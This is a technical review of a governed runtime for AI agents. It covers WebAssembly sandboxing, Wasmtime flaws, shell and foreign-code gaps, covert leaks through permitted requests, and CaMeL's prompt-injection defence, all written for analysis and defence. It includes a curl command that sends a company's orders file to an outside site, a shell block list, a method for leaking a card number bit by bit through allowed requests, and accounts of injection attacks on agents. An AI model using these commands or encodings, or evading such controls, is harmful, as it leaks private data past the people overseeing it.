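| Native extensions | Load machine code into the virtual machine's own process | Machine code does not obey the virtual machine's rules |
| External processes | Start another program and exchange messages with it | The other program does the work |
| Loading new bytecode | Add a module to the running system | The module arrives after the check |

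Erlang has these facilities for good reasons. For example, engineers can load new bytecode to repair a busy server without stopping it. But an import list covers only the dependencies a module names in advance, and all five facilities let code reach something it has not named.

A better checker could search for uses of the facilities themselves. McCann expects this to catch most attempts, but an author can disguise such a call, and could respond to each new search rule with another disguise. By Rice's theorem, no checker can decide correctly for every program whether it will have an external effect. A cautious checker could reject everything it cannot show to be harmless, but McCann argues, without giving measurements, that it would reject most ordinary Elixir code. Joe-E's designers accepted a similar drawback when they restricted Java, and still wrote a working web server. McCann restricts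 the compiled code instead, so the same rules apply to every source language that compiles to it.

### Removing the power from compiled code

The remedy starts with compiling executors to WebAssembly, where a module can call only its own functions and its declared imports. The module refers to functions by number, so it cannot reach a new one by computing its name. It can choose a function while running, but only from a table of its own functions and those the host has supplied. WebAssembly has no instruction for evaluating source text, loading a native library, starting a process or loading another module. These limits close all five gaps unless an import reopens one.

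McCann therefore permits only imports on a fixed list. Some of the listed functions handle data, such as text, numbers and the step's context, and others construct effect requests. For example, the function for web requests adds a description of the request to a list, which the mediator reads after the executor has finished.

The list excludes WASI, the standard interface that WebAssembly modules use to access files, sockets, clocks and random numbers. A module that imports any function outside the list fails the check, so an executor cannot read the clock, although Mashin's `compute` expressions can.

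A program called the certifier then creates a *purity certificate* for each executor. It lists the module's imports and labels each one as permitted or not. McCann calls this list a purity proof, but it contains no logical argument. The certifier hashes the module and the list, and signs the two hashes with a private key. Anyone with the matching public key can check the signature.

Before an executor runs, a gate in the runtime makes six checks and stops at the first failure:

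1. The signature is valid for this module and this list of imports.
2. The module's hash matches the one in the certificate.
3. The list's hash matches the one in the certificate.
4. The imports in the module itself match the list.
5. Every import is on the current list of permitted functions.
6. The certifier's conclusion was "pure".

The gate reads the imports from the module itself and does not rely on the certifier's description. If someone stole the certifier's key and signed a module that imports a network function, the gate would still find the import and reject the module. McCann warns that such a thief could get round the gate entirely, which understates the protection his design gives.

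The signature matters more outside the company. An auditor who has the certificate but not the module cannot repeat the fourth check and has to trust the certifier. For work between companies, McCann adds a second signature, in which the host states which engine and list of permitted functions it used. But a host with an altered mediator could sign the same statement. He leaves adding hashes of the runtime itself for later, and even those would be unreliable if the altered runtime reported them.

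McCann proved this paper's theorems by hand, so they do not have the machine-checked status of his results about the mediator.

### The `call` executor

Suppose that a refund agent's program needs to run the `send_refund` machine for $120. The `call` executor turns that step into a request. McCann wrote it in 147 lines of Rust, which compile to a 121-kilobyte WebAssembly module with four imports:

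- `get_input_len` returns the length of the input.
- `get_input` copies the input into the module's memory.
- `set_output` passes the result and any requests back to the host.
- `log` sends a message to the host's log.

The gate takes a median of 49 microseconds to verify the module, and stores its decision for later runs. The host then creates a fresh instance of the module, passes it the name `send_refund` and the amount, and gets back a request to call that machine. This takes 398 microseconds. `call` cannot run `send_refund` itself, so `send_refund` doesn't run until the mediator has checked the request. The ledger entry includes the certificate's hash, so an auditor can later identify which executor produced the request.

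Checking and recording add 535 microseconds, bringing the total to about 0.93 milliseconds, nearly as long as a fast database query. The 398 microseconds depends on keeping compiled machine code in a cache. Without the cache, each run takes about 5.5 milliseconds. The certificate covers the WebAssembly module but not the cached machine code, so the runtime must also protect the cache from tampering.

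The fourth import, `log`, breaks McCann's rule that permitted functions must send no information to external systems. It passes text chosen by the executor to the host's log without a policy check or a ledger entry. Many companies forward their logs to an outside monitoring service, which would send this text outside the company. The fix is simple, since `call` could return its log messages with its other requests. The mistake is similar to the one in E, where a review found unsafe Java methods on the approved list, though the list here is much shorter. If the list's maintainers removed `log`, the gate would reject `call` until someone rebuilt it.

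Another of the four executors, `code`, shows how little a certificate may cover. It returns a request to evaluate some code, which the host then runs outside the certified module. The certificate guarantees that `code` can only return this request, and doesn't cover what the host runs.

### What remains to be trusted

A fault in any of McCann's five trusted components could break the guarantee.

| Trusted component | What a fault could do |
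|---|---|
| Wasmtime, the WebAssembly engine | Let a module reach memory or functions outside its sandbox |
| The functions supplied to modules | Cause an external effect while appearing to handle data |
| The list of permitted functions | Include a function that has external effects, as it does with `log` |
| The gate | Admit a module with a forbidden import |
| The mediator | Perform a request without checking it |

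He counts about 37 executor modules with 17,000 lines of code that people previously had to trust, plus any that outsiders might write later. Moving them all to WebAssembly would remove the need to trust them, but people would have to trust Wasmtime instead. Its maintainers have put thousands of hours into each of its two main compilers. Wasmtime is far too large to meet Anderson's requirement that people be able to analyse the monitor completely.

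The table leaves out Wasmex, the Erlang virtual machine and the operating system. Wasmex is an Elixir library that loads Wasmtime into the virtual machine's process as a native extension, so a defence against native extensions itself relies on a native extension. McCann's definition does not include the certifier, although he writes that it does.

The guarantee does not cover availability either. A certified executor can loop forever or use up memory, so the host has to limit its time, memory and number of instructions.

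### Three trust tiers

Most of Mashin's executors cannot move to WebAssembly yet, because no compiler translates Elixir into it. McCann therefore sorts executors into three tiers, which are separate from the mediator's six trust levels:

- **Tier 1, verified purity.** The executor is a WebAssembly module with a valid certificate.
- **Tier 2, static analysis.** The executor runs on the Erlang virtual machine after passing the import check.
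- **Tier 3, experimental.** The executor runs on the Erlang virtual machine without any such check, and is for development only.

Mashin's own Elixir executors are in Tier 2, so the five gaps still apply to them. Only the four executors that McCann built in Rust (`call`, `code`, `memory` and `reason`) can reach Tier 1. He considers Tier 2 adequate for code that a trusted team writes for its own use, but wants Tier 1 for code from outsiders.

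The runtime checks an executor's tier before running it and records the tier in the ledger. A company can also set a minimum tier for each program. Tier 2 and Tier 3 executors share a virtual machine with the code that enforces these rules, so a hostile one that could load new bytecode might replace the gate or the mediator, although McCann describes the enforcement as impossible to bypass. Setting a Tier 1 minimum for the refund program would not help if a Tier 3 experiment ran in the same virtual machine. Mixing Joe-E with unrestricted Java causes the same problem. A company can rely on Tier 1 only if it keeps the lower tiers out of the virtual machine.

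### Wasmtime's security record

At the end of 2025, Wasmtime looked like a safe choice. Debian, a Linux distribution that tracks flaws in the software it packages, lists four Wasmtime vulnerabilities for that year. The Wasmtime project rated all four low severity in its release notices, the last of which was Crichton's *Upcoming Security Release for Wasmtime on 2025-11-11* (2025). GitLab's *Advisories for Cargo/Wasmtime package* includes three of them. Two could crash the host, and the third was an unsafe programming interface that could let two threads interfere with each other's use of memory.

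By 20 November 2026, Debian listed 56 vulnerabilities for the year, 14 times as many, plus four entries without an official number. Many let a module crash or stall the host. At least five flaws in 2026, including one announced in December, were rated critical, the highest standard severity rating.

| Announced in 2026 | Critical flaws | Severity out of 10 | Where they applied | Possible consequence |
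|---|---|---|---|---|
| 9 April | 2 | 9.0 each | One in an optional compiler, one in the default compiler on ARM64 processors | Escape from the sandbox |
| 19 October | 2 | 9.9 each | The default compiler, one on all processors and one on ARM64 only | Escape from the sandbox |
| 4 December | 1 | 9.8 | The default compiler | An attacker's code running on the host, or a crash |

The Bytecode Alliance, which maintains Wasmtime, published the April figures in *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (2026). The October figures come from The Hacker News' *Two Critical Wasmtime Flaws Could Let Malicious WebAssembly Modules Escape Sandboxes* (2026), and the December figures come from OffSeq's *wasmtime · Cranelift* (2026). The maintainers released fixes each time. As of 26 October, they had not reported any attacks that used the October flaws.

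Wasmtime's developers searched the code with teams of AI agents for three weeks before the April release, and found 11 of the 12 flaws fixed in it. According to the Bytecode Alliance, some of the flaws had been there for a long time. Few flaws were recorded in 2025 partly because search methods were weaker, so the increase does not mean that Wasmtime suddenly got worse. But a search that stops finding flaws is poor evidence that none are left. The developers found nothing new in the last week of their search, yet Debian lists another 40 vulnerabilities between then and 20 November.

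One of April's critical flaws also shows how a proof can go out of date. Researchers had formally verified the rules by which Cranelift, Wasmtime's default compiler, translates WebAssembly into machine instructions. The developers later introduced the flaw by changing the rules without updating the formal model. When they updated the model, the verification tool found the same flaw as the AI agents. The proof had been correct, but only for an older version of the compiler. McCann's proofs could go out of date in the same way whenever someone changes the Mashin runtime.

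An attacker has to get Wasmtime to compile a module they control to use either of the October flaws. Mashin's gate restricts which modules reach the engine, but it checks them by their imports, and a module can exploit a compiler flaw without any suspicious imports. The certifier in McCann's build process signs any module whose imports are all permitted, so it would sign such a module. The danger is small for executors that a company wrote itself and greatest for executors from outsiders, for which McCann most recommends certified purity.

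The ARM64 flaw announced in October affected every Wasmtime release before the fixes. McCann ran his measurements on an Apple M-series computer, which has an ARM64 processor, so his test system almost certainly contained the flaw. The flaw doesn't invalidate his theorem, which assumes that Wasmtime works correctly. But his claim that certain bypasses are "structurally impossible" depends on Wasmtime, a large and often-repaired program, having no relevant bug.

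Excluding WASI turned out to be a good decision. RustSec's *Filesystem sandbox escape when paths or symlinks contain trailing slashes* (2026) describes a flaw with a severity of 8.8 in the way Wasmtime confines modules to certain files. Another flaw, listed in GitLab's *Advisories for Cargo/Wasmtime-Wasi package*, let a module overwrite a file that it had permission only to read. Both require access to files through WASI, so an executor that the gate had admitted could not exploit either. A short list of imports cannot prevent compiler flaws, but it keeps modules away from much other code that could contain mistakes.

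Operators also have to update promptly. Wasmtime's maintainers support most releases for two months and every twelfth one for two years, according to The Hacker News. Releases outside those periods did not get the October fixes. A company running Mashin would depend on Wasmex's maintainers to adopt each fixed version of Wasmtime, and then on Mashin's maintainers to adopt the new Wasmex.

### A process without network rights

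A second barrier could limit the damage if a module broke out of Wasmtime. In the current design, the escaped module would be inside the process that also runs the mediator and performs approved actions. McCann leaves splitting this process in two for later. One process would hold the WebAssembly engine and the functions it supplies, with no right to use files or the network, and the other would hold the mediator. If an escaped module then tried to open a network connection, the operating system would refuse.

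The split would be even more useful for Tier 2 executors. A company could run them in a separate Erlang virtual machine with the same restrictions, and code could no longer reach the network through the five gaps. A dynamic call might reach the function for opening a connection, but the function would fail. On Linux, the same system call filter would apply to native code in the process and any program it started. This would protect Elixir code without waiting for a compiler to WebAssembly, although the virtual machine would still need a channel to the mediator.

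If several programs shared the restricted process, an escaped module could read their data and submit requests in their names. For example, a module from an untrusted program could pose as the refund agent and ask for a payment. Giving each program its own process would prevent this, provided that the mediator identified the sender by its process rather than by a name supplied in the request. Each process would use some memory, and each request would have to pass between processes. McCann has not measured this overhead.

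With two barriers, an attacker needs a usable flaw in both at the same time. Suppose each barrier has an unpatched flaw for 18 days a year, or about 5 percent of the time. If the two periods are independent, both barriers have one at the same time about 0.25 percent of the time, or less than one day a year.

Real flaws may not be so independent, since the same AI tools can search both barriers. On 19 October 2026, the day Wasmtime's maintainers announced two critical flaws, *PwnEscape vulnerability lets you escape KVM* (Cimpanu, 2026) reported a Linux kernel flaw that let code break out of a virtual machine, which cloud companies often use as a stronger barrier than an ordinary process. According to The Hacker News' *Critical PwnEscape Linux Kernel Vulnerability Lets Guest VMs Read Host Memory* (2026), the flaw exposed host memory in the live sandboxes of Vercel, a web hosting company. Running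 code on the host worked only in laboratory tests. The kernel's developers had already released a patch, but an operator slow to update could have had known flaws in both the engine and the kernel that week.

The mediator's process must keep its network access to perform the approved actions. An escaped module could send it malformed requests to exploit a bug in the code that reads them, which could let an attacker past both barriers. That code should therefore be small and reject anything that does not exactly match the expected format.

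## What happens when a program needs foreign code or writes new code?

A flaw in Wasmtime is accidental, but the designers of most languages deliberately let programs run code that the language's own rules may not cover. They do this because programmers want to call existing C libraries, run Python scripts, and execute code that did not exist when the program started.

### Inside a native call

A *foreign function interface* lets a program call functions written in another language, usually C. The programmer declares the function's name and argument types. The operating system loads the C library's machine code into the program's process, and each call converts the arguments to C's format and jumps to that code. The calling language's runtime checks nothing until the function returns.

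Suppose the refund program used a C library to produce PDF receipts, and the library ran in the same process as the mediator. The library could make the `connect` system call itself and send a receipt anywhere, without an effect request. It could also write to any writable memory in the process, including the memory that holds the $500 refund limit and the mediator's unsaved ledger entries. A faulty library might change the limit by accident if it wrote a few bytes past the end of a buffer, and the mediator would then enforce the wrong limit. A single native call can therefore undo every guarantee above it, because they all depend on other code being unable to alter the runtime's memory.

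Programs in scripting languages routinely call native code. As *Bilingual Problems* (2021) explains, the package managers npm, pip and gem can compile a package's native extension during installation, and the interpreter later loads it into its own process. Highly skilled developers usually write the language's own native code, but anyone can publish an extension.

A wrapper can hide a C library behind functions that appear to follow the calling language's rules. Rust's compiler normally guarantees that a program never uses memory after freeing it, but code marked `unsafe` can do things the compiler does not check, such as calling foreign functions. In *Agentic Discovery of Soundness Bugs in Safe Rust Bindings*, Momeu and Sen (2026) call a wrapper *sound* if no program written entirely in safe Rust can cause undefined behaviour through it. Undefined behaviour is behaviour for which the language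 guarantees nothing.

Their first example of an unsound wrapper is `ssh2`, which gives Rust programs access to a C library for secure remote logins. Its `auth_methods` function returns text stored in a buffer that the C library owns and frees on the next call. A program that calls the function twice and then prints the first result reads freed memory. The compiler accepts this program, even with a setting that forbids unsafe code, because the wrapper's types do not state that the text is valid only until the next call.

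Momeu and Sen had AI agents audit 19 widely used Rust packages, most of them wrappers for C and C++ libraries such as OpenSSL and SQLite. The agents found 213 bugs that cause undefined behaviour, about 11 per package. The median audit cost less than $50, so an attacker could afford the same search. Many such bugs appear only when a program uses the wrapper in a way its author did not anticipate. Ordinary programmers seldom write such programs, but a governed language has to withstand programmers who are trying to get around its restrictions.

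### How often programmers use the exits

Rust makes this easy to measure because programmers have to mark such code with the keyword `unsafe`. In January 2023, 21,506 of the 103,516 packages in Rust's public collection used it, or 20.8 percent, according to *Is unsafe an Achilles' Heel?* (2023). In May 2024, 19.11 percent of about 127,000 packages with significant code used it, and 34.35 percent directly called another package that did, according to the Rust Foundation's *Unsafe Rust in the Wild*.

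*Is Rust Used Safely by Software Developers?* (2020) reported that fewer than 30 percent of Rust libraries used unsafe code themselves, but that more than half relied on unsafe code somewhere in their dependencies, so the compiler could not fully check them. The second figure is the most relevant to a governed language, because unchecked code anywhere in a program's dependencies can break a guarantee about the whole program.

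Most uses of `unsafe` are calls to code in other languages, according to the Rust Foundation. The 2023 study emphasizes type conversions, manual memory management and unchecked indexing, but it searched for 140 known function names, which would miss most calls to foreign libraries. A language that manages memory automatically has little need for those functions, but its users still want foreign libraries.

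These figures show that about one Rust package in five bypasses compiler checks, even though many people choose the language for those checks. The figures do not measure ungoverned effects, because Rust code can open a network connection without the `unsafe` keyword. They also count an abandoned package the same as a popular one.

Python requires no such keyword, so native code is harder to find. *Cross-Ecosystem Vulnerability Analysis for Python Applications* (2026) explains that a wheel, Python's ready-built package format, can contain both native extensions and copies of libraries from other projects. About half of the packages that ship such libraries use a standard tool, `auditwheel`, to include them, and the rest rely on their own build scripts. A reviewer who reads only the Python source will miss this code. *A Comprehensive Study of Native Code Bugs in Python Applications* (2026)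 covers 1,039 bugs in the native code of Python projects on GitHub, but this count does not measure what share of packages have such bugs.

### One permission that includes the others

Mashin's `exec` step runs Python, JavaScript or shell code as a single request and needs the permission `execute_shell_commands`. The mediator checks that request but not what the code does once it is running.

A program that prepares a monthly report might declare these permissions:

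```
ensures
  permissions
    allowed to execute_shell_commands
    not allowed to http, db_write
```

Its `exec` step could run this command:

```
curl --data @orders.csv https://files.example.net
```

The mediator allows the request because the program has permission to run commands, and adds one entry to the ledger. The `curl` program then sends the company's orders to a website. The ban on `http` has no effect because the Mashin program never submitted an HTTP request. In practice, `execute_shell_commands` includes every power that the operating system gives the started program, even those that other permissions forbid.

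In this case an auditor could at least read the command in the ledger. If the command were `python report.py`, the entry would contain the script's name but not its contents, and someone could change the script afterwards.

In Mashin, untrusted code cannot run commands, but McCann's specification allows even code at the "tested" trust level, the second-lowest of six, to run them if the program declares the permission.

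Filtering commands by their text is a weak remedy. *An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents* (2026) includes the description of a shell tool that by default blocks `rm -rf`, `sudo`, `git push` and a few other commands, and requires approval for everything else. But a Python script can delete a folder without using `rm`, and whoever approves the script may see only its name. The description lists the tool's side effects as "anything the command does" and states that the tool does not track which files changed. It suggests running `git status` afterwards, which can reveal changed files in the project but not a network connection.

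### Leave it out, confine it or compile it

The simplest response is to have no general-purpose request. The two longer examples in Mashin's guide to governance both deny `execute_shell_commands`. A company that needs PDF receipts could instead define a `make_receipt` request, which takes an order number and an amount, and put the PDF library behind it. The mediator could then check a readable request instead of a script, but somebody would have to build such a request for every library the company needs. If the library ran inside the mediator's process, a faulty write could still change the refund limit again.

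A second response is to let the program start foreign code but have the operating system confine it. The program could request that a script be allowed to read `orders.csv` and write `receipt.pdf`, with no network access. The mediator would still make one decision and record one entry, but the entry would now include the limits on what the script can do. Existing Python code, including native extensions, could run unchanged as long as it needed no other access.

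Within those limits, the script's file operations would still happen without individual checks or records, so they would not be governed effects in the strict sense. The runtime could avoid this by giving the script private copies of its input files and discarding everything it writes except the receipt. Only a separate, checked request would copy the receipt out. If a script needed a web page partway through, someone would have to rewrite it to request the page from the mediator.

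The third response, which McCann proposes for certified executors, is to compile foreign code to WebAssembly and allow it only the same list of permitted imports. He names existing tools for Python, Rust and C. A memory error in a C library would then damage only that module's own memory. The error could still make the module request a refund of the wrong amount, but the request would go through the mediator.

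Turning every outside action into a separate request gives the finest control but requires the most changes to existing code. C programs compiled to WebAssembly usually import functions for files and clocks, and Mashin's gate rejects modules with such imports. Someone would have to replace those functions with ones that only produce requests.

An executor also can't receive a reply to a request while it is running, because the mediator reads its requests only after it has finished. A programmer who wants a Python script to download a page and then search it would have to split the script in two, with the downloaded page as the second part's input.

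McCann treats compiling and certifying foreign code as a separate build step. This works for a library that exists in advance, but not for a script that an agent writes while running. Pyodide, the tool he names for Python, could help because it is a complete Python interpreter compiled to WebAssembly. If someone adapted it to use only permitted imports, the company could certify the interpreter once and pass it each new script as data. The scripts would not need their own certificates, because they could do only what the interpreter could do.

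### Programs as data

An agent can also write new programs in Mashin itself. *Governed Metaprogramming for Intelligent Systems* (McCann, 2026) separates describing such a program from running it. A *machine form* is a data value that describes a Mashin program as a tree of its steps and settings. Code can build a form with `quote`, which captures program text without running it, or get the current program's form with `reflect()`. It can then change the form, compare two versions or calculate a hash. All of this is pure computation and needs no permission.

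In McCann's example, a program uses a language model to classify text and also receives the model's confidence. If the confidence is below 0.7, the program edits its own form to name a stronger model. The edited form is only data, so for the change to take effect, the program has to request *materialization*, McCann's term for turning a form into a program that can run.

Depending on the request, the runtime executes the form once or registers it as a new version of the program. For a new version, a separate ledger records the old and new hashes, the differences and the evidence for the change. Mashin's *Lesson 10* shows that calling `form.eval()` from a `compute` step causes a compiler error with instructions to use an `ask` step.

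McCann justifies the check by arguing that granting power is itself an effect. Materialization grants power because a form cannot send a message or spend money, but a running program may be able to.

### Two rules and the case between them

McCann defines materialization with two rules. Here σ is the set of permissions that the requesting program holds, and needs(f) is the set that the steps in form f require:

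```
Approve:  materialize(f)  →  a program that can run, and a record
          if f passes inspection and needs(f) ⊆ σ

Reject:   materialize(f)  →  no program, and a record with the reason
          if f fails inspection
```

The inspection checks the form against the policy. The form may require only permissions that the policy allows and use only approved language models. It must also meet structural rules, such as a maximum number of steps, and its estimated cost must be within the budget. Each check examines a finite tree, so the inspection always finishes. McCann reports that the inspection takes less than 100 microseconds for a typical program.

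The Approve and Reject rules leave out one case. Suppose the policy allows programs to use `http`, but a text classifier holds only `llm_call`, the permission to call language models. The classifier writes a program that sends web requests. The program passes inspection, which compares it with the policy and not with the classifier's permissions. The Approve rule does not apply because the classifier lacks `http`, and the Reject rule does not apply because the program passed inspection. The program cannot run, which is safe, but the attempt is not recorded, although McCann writes that materialization always produces a record. A third rule that rejected such programs would fix this.

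The working inspector makes six checks, which cover the form's structure, required fields, permissions, language models and trust level, and whether it has a governance section. McCann's description does not make clear whether the permission check uses the policy's list or the author's. If it uses only the policy's list and nothing else makes the comparison with σ, the classifier could give its new program web access. The six checks also omit the cost estimate from the formal definition.

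McCann points out that nobody can inspect generated code in this way if it is an opaque string. `exec` steps have this problem because they contain Python or shell code as text. The inspector can establish little more than that a form with such a step needs `execute_shell_commands`.

### Would an unrestricted `eval` be a way out?

Many languages have an operation, often called `eval`, that runs program text or data as code. McCann argues that an unchecked `eval` would let a program escape its restrictions by writing and running another program that lacks them. Whether he is right depends on which permissions the new program receives.

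Programmers do not need `eval` to run a program description, because they can write an interpreter. An agent might produce this list of steps as ordinary data:

```
[{do: post, to: "https://payments.example.com/refunds",
  with: {order: "A-1041", amount: 120}},
 {do: exec, to: "shell", with: "python report.py"}]
```

In the notation of McCann's calculus, with functions added, the central line of an interpreter for such lists would be:

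```
run(step) = ask(step.do, step.to, step.with)
```

The rest of the interpreter is pure code that goes through the list and keeps the replies. When it reaches the refund, it can only submit a request, which the mediator checks against the permissions of the program that contains the interpreter. If that program lacks permission to run commands, the mediator rejects the second step. The list gives the agent no new powers, whatever it contains.

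People can write an interpreter in any language that can compute anything computable. McCann's invariant that no callable operation turns a program description into an executing program is therefore false for any such language, if taken literally. It can be true only of programs that the runtime itself compiles and treats as separate machines with their own permissions. His machine-checked theorem also covers only such machines. It states that pure code cannot produce one, which follows almost directly from the assumption that pure code has no `eval`.

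An `eval` that ran new code under the permissions of the program that wrote it would be faster than the interpreter but no more dangerous. `eval` adds power if the new code can receive a permission that the program writing it lacked. This could easily happen in Mashin, because each program's file declares its own permissions and guards.

| Author's situation | New program | Run by an interpreter | Run by an unchecked `eval` that accepts the new declarations | Under McCann's rules |
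|---|---|---|---|---|
| Holds `http` | Uses `http` | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed if it passes inspection |
| Lacks permission to run commands | Declares that permission | Refused | Allowed | Does not run |
| Needs approval for each web request | Declares `http` without approval | Waits for approval | Allowed at once | Unclear, because σ is a plain set of permissions |
| Has a guard that removes personal data | Has no guard | Guard still applies | No guard | Allowed unless the policy requires the guard |

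The last two rows show that comparing sets of permissions is not enough. A new program can hold the same permissions as its author and still be more powerful because it has dropped a condition attached to one of them. The comparison also misses differences in trust level and in the setting that switches off ledger entries. A safer rule would require the new program to keep all of its author's conditions and have no higher trust level than its author, unless an operator decided otherwise.

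An `eval` that accepts text in the host's language poses a different danger because the new code could act without making requests. The same is true of runtime evaluation on the Erlang virtual machine.

The interpreter also limits what inspection can achieve. If the inspector rejects a form for having too many steps, the agent can give the same steps to an interpreter. The mediator will still check each request, but nobody will have inspected the plan, and the ledger will not contain its hash. Any rule that must never be broken therefore has to apply to individual requests as well as to forms.

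Inspection is still useful for honest programs because it can reject a plan before the first step runs. Without it, an interpreter might pay a refund before the mediator blocks the step that updates the customer's record. Inspection matters more for a new version than for a single run, because a new version stays in use after its author has finished, and other people may run it without knowing that a program wrote it.

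## What can still get out through permitted requests?

If the mediator checks every request, no program runs foreign code, and nothing in the runtime, Wasmtime or the operating system fails, the refund agent can act only through requests that the policy allows. But the agent still chooses the data in those requests, and the systems that receive them can take further actions. The number and timing of the requests can also reveal a secret.

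### Secrets inside an allowed request

The refund agent needs exchange rates for foreign customers, so the policy lets it fetch pages from a currency service. A normal request ends with a currency code. If the agent puts a customer's card number there instead, the mediator still allows the request because the action and target are both permitted, and the service's owner can read the number in the server's logs.

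McCann concedes in *Certified Purity for Cognitive Workflow Executors* that an executor can put a secret in a web address and still count as pure, because purity concerns whether code can act, not what its requests contain. He leaves such leaks to Mashin's guards, which can recognise a card number in plain text but not one that the program has encrypted. The policy language in his proofs cannot detect such leaks, because *Effect-Transparent Governance for AI Workflow Architectures* defines its rules to test only trust levels and permissions.

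A stricter format reduces how much each request can leak. If the mediator accepts only real currency codes, no request can contain a card number, but the agent still chooses which code to send. With 128 permitted codes, each choice can convey seven bits. A 16-digit card number contains about 53 bits, so eight requests would be enough to send it.

### Labels on data

*Information flow control* is the main defence against this kind of leak. It checks whether a particular value may be sent to a particular destination, whereas a permission only determines whether the program may send at all. To do this, the runtime labels every value and works out the label of each result from the labels of its inputs.

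Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, use two marks in their basic examples, S for secret and U for untrusted. A label is a set of marks, so there are four possible labels. Two rules govern them:

```
Combining:  a result computed from values labelled a and b has the label a ⊔ b
Sending:    a value labelled a may go to a destination with limit m only if a ⊑ m
```

When labels are sets of marks, a ⊔ b contains every mark in a or b. The relation a ⊑ m, read "a may flow to m", means that m includes every mark in a. Suppose the payment company may receive secrets but must not act on untrusted data, and the currency service may receive anything except secrets.

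| Value | Label | To the payment company (limit: S) | To the currency service (limit: U) |
|---|---|---|---|
| A currency code in the program's text | None | Allowed | Allowed |
| A customer's card number | S | Allowed | Refused |
| An account number from an incoming email | U | Refused | Allowed |
| Text that combines the card number and the email | S and U | Refused | Refused |

A permission check would give the same answer for all four values in each column. Encrypting the card number does not help the agent either. The program computes the encrypted text from the number, so the text keeps the S mark.

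The runtime also has to label as secret anything a program does because of a test on a secret. For example, if a program picks a currency code according to a digit of the card number, the code reveals the digit without containing it. The goal is *noninterference*, which means that two runs with the same public inputs but different secrets should produce the same public outputs.

Useful programs need exceptions. A receipt may show the last four digits of a card, so someone has to authorise removing the S mark from those digits. Each exception is a possible leak, but reviewers can find it in the program's text.

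McCann calls information flow control complementary to his design and suggests combining the two, but his calculus has no labels. Adding labels to a language for AI agents is a problem because a language model's reply may depend on anything in the conversation, so it must receive every label in it. After the refund agent reads one email from a customer, everything it writes is labeled untrusted, so it can no longer pay anyone.

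### How CaMeL tracks where values come from

CaMeL, presented in 2025 by researchers at Google DeepMind and elsewhere, addresses this problem with two language models. It defends against *prompt injection*, in which an attacker plants instructions in text that an agent reads. Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that a privileged model reads only the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. A quarantined model reads emails and web pages and extracts values, but it cannot use any tools.

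For a refund, the privileged model might write:

```python
email = get_last_email()
account = query_quarantined_model("Find the account number", email)
send_refund(order="A-1041", account=account)
```

CaMeL runs this program in its own interpreter, which records that `account` came from `email`. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the arguments and their origins against that tool's policy. The policy for `send_refund` might allow an account number the user supplied but require the user's approval for one from an email.

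Instructions in the email cannot add a step, because the privileged model finished the program without reading the email. But they can still cause the quarantined model to return the attacker's account number. Willison's earlier two-model proposal had this weakness, and CaMeL's policies address it by checking where the number came from.

### What the protection costs

Most tests of CaMeL use AgentDojo, the set of office, travel and banking tasks on which Tiffany and colleagues tested Sapien. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, could not fully reproduce CaMeL's results, so they give its published figures. With OpenAI's GPT-4o, no attacks succeeded against CaMeL, while 57.7 percent succeeded against an agent without defences, but CaMeL completed far fewer tasks. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, cite a higher completion rate of 67 percent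 but don't name the model.

Researchers ran CaMeL again in 2026. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) tested CaMeL's strictest mode, *SecureClaw* (2026) used an adapted version, and Garby and colleagues ran only the banking tasks.

| Source of the figures | Tasks completed with CaMeL | Tasks completed in a comparison run | Successful attacks on CaMeL |
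|---|---|---|---|
| Published figures, GPT-4o | 53.6% | 83.0%, no defence | 0% |
| Choi and colleagues, GPT-5.2 | 36.5% | 86.5%, no defence | 0 of 108 |
| *SecureClaw* | 29.9% | 60.8%, its own defence | 0 of 629 |
| Garby and colleagues, GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 66.7%, CaMeL without policies | 0 of 231 |

The results showing zero successful attacks are less impressive than they look. *MetaPermit* (2026) examined a further set of runs and found that CaMeL often blocked the attack but left the user's task unfinished. Newer models also resist the older attacks without any added defense, and only 0.2 percent of those attacks succeeded against the undefended agent that Choi and colleagues tested. Bhagwatkar and colleagues also stopped every attack with a simple filter that rewrites tool replies, but they then got some attacks past the filter by adapting them to it.

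The 108 attacks in the table are better evidence for tracking where data comes from. They disguise false data as trusted details, such as the sender of an email, and 49.1 percent of them worked on the undefended agent. CaMeL let 25 percent through when it used two models but no policies, and only its strictest tracking stopped all 108.

CaMeL also uses more computing. Bhagwatkar and colleagues report that the median task takes 2.82 times as many input tokens (the units of text a model processes) and 2.73 times as many output tokens. Their averages imply 3.6 and 6.1 times as many, so a few tasks must use far more tokens than the rest.

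### Where the labels went missing

CaMeL's normal mode let 23.1 percent of the disguised-data attacks through. Choi and colleagues traced this to a bug that removed the untrusted label from values the quarantined model extracted.

Garby and colleagues found two subtler gaps. Suppose a program first records a customer as rich, then changes the record if the balance turns out to be low. If the balance is high, the record doesn't change, so CaMeL doesn't mark it as secret, even though it now reveals that the balance is high. The other gap is in an ordinary Python loop that runs outside CaMeL's interpreter and retries failed programs. Whether a policy blocks a program can depend on a secret, and that result reaches the loop without a label. Each such leak reveals only one bit, but repeated retries could reveal the whole secret.

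Garby and colleagues' own language, LLMbda, puts the retry loop inside the labelled program. They proved a form of noninterference for every program in the language, including agents that write and run code. Because a language model's replies are random, the theorem concerns the probabilities of public results. It does not cover what an observer learns when a program fails to finish. They wrote the interpreter in the proof assistant Lean, and their theorems describe the same program that calls the language model. McCann, by contrast, only tested whether Mashin's runtime matches his model.

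With the checks always on, their agent completed 36 of 48 banking runs using GPT-5.2, twice as many as CaMeL with its policies. The agent tests its plan in a simulated world until the plan works, so errors caused by real data never influence a retry. It may also mark values as trusted if it chooses them before reading any outside data. Without that option, the completion rate with another model, Qwen3.7-plus, fell from 75 to 62.5 percent. The 48 runs cover only 16 different tasks, so all these percentages are rough.

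Only two of 1,296 attacks succeeded, both on a task in which the user asked the agent to pay the bill in a file and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Refusing all payments based on files would stop this attack but also block the legitimate task, because the real bill and the false one come from the same file.

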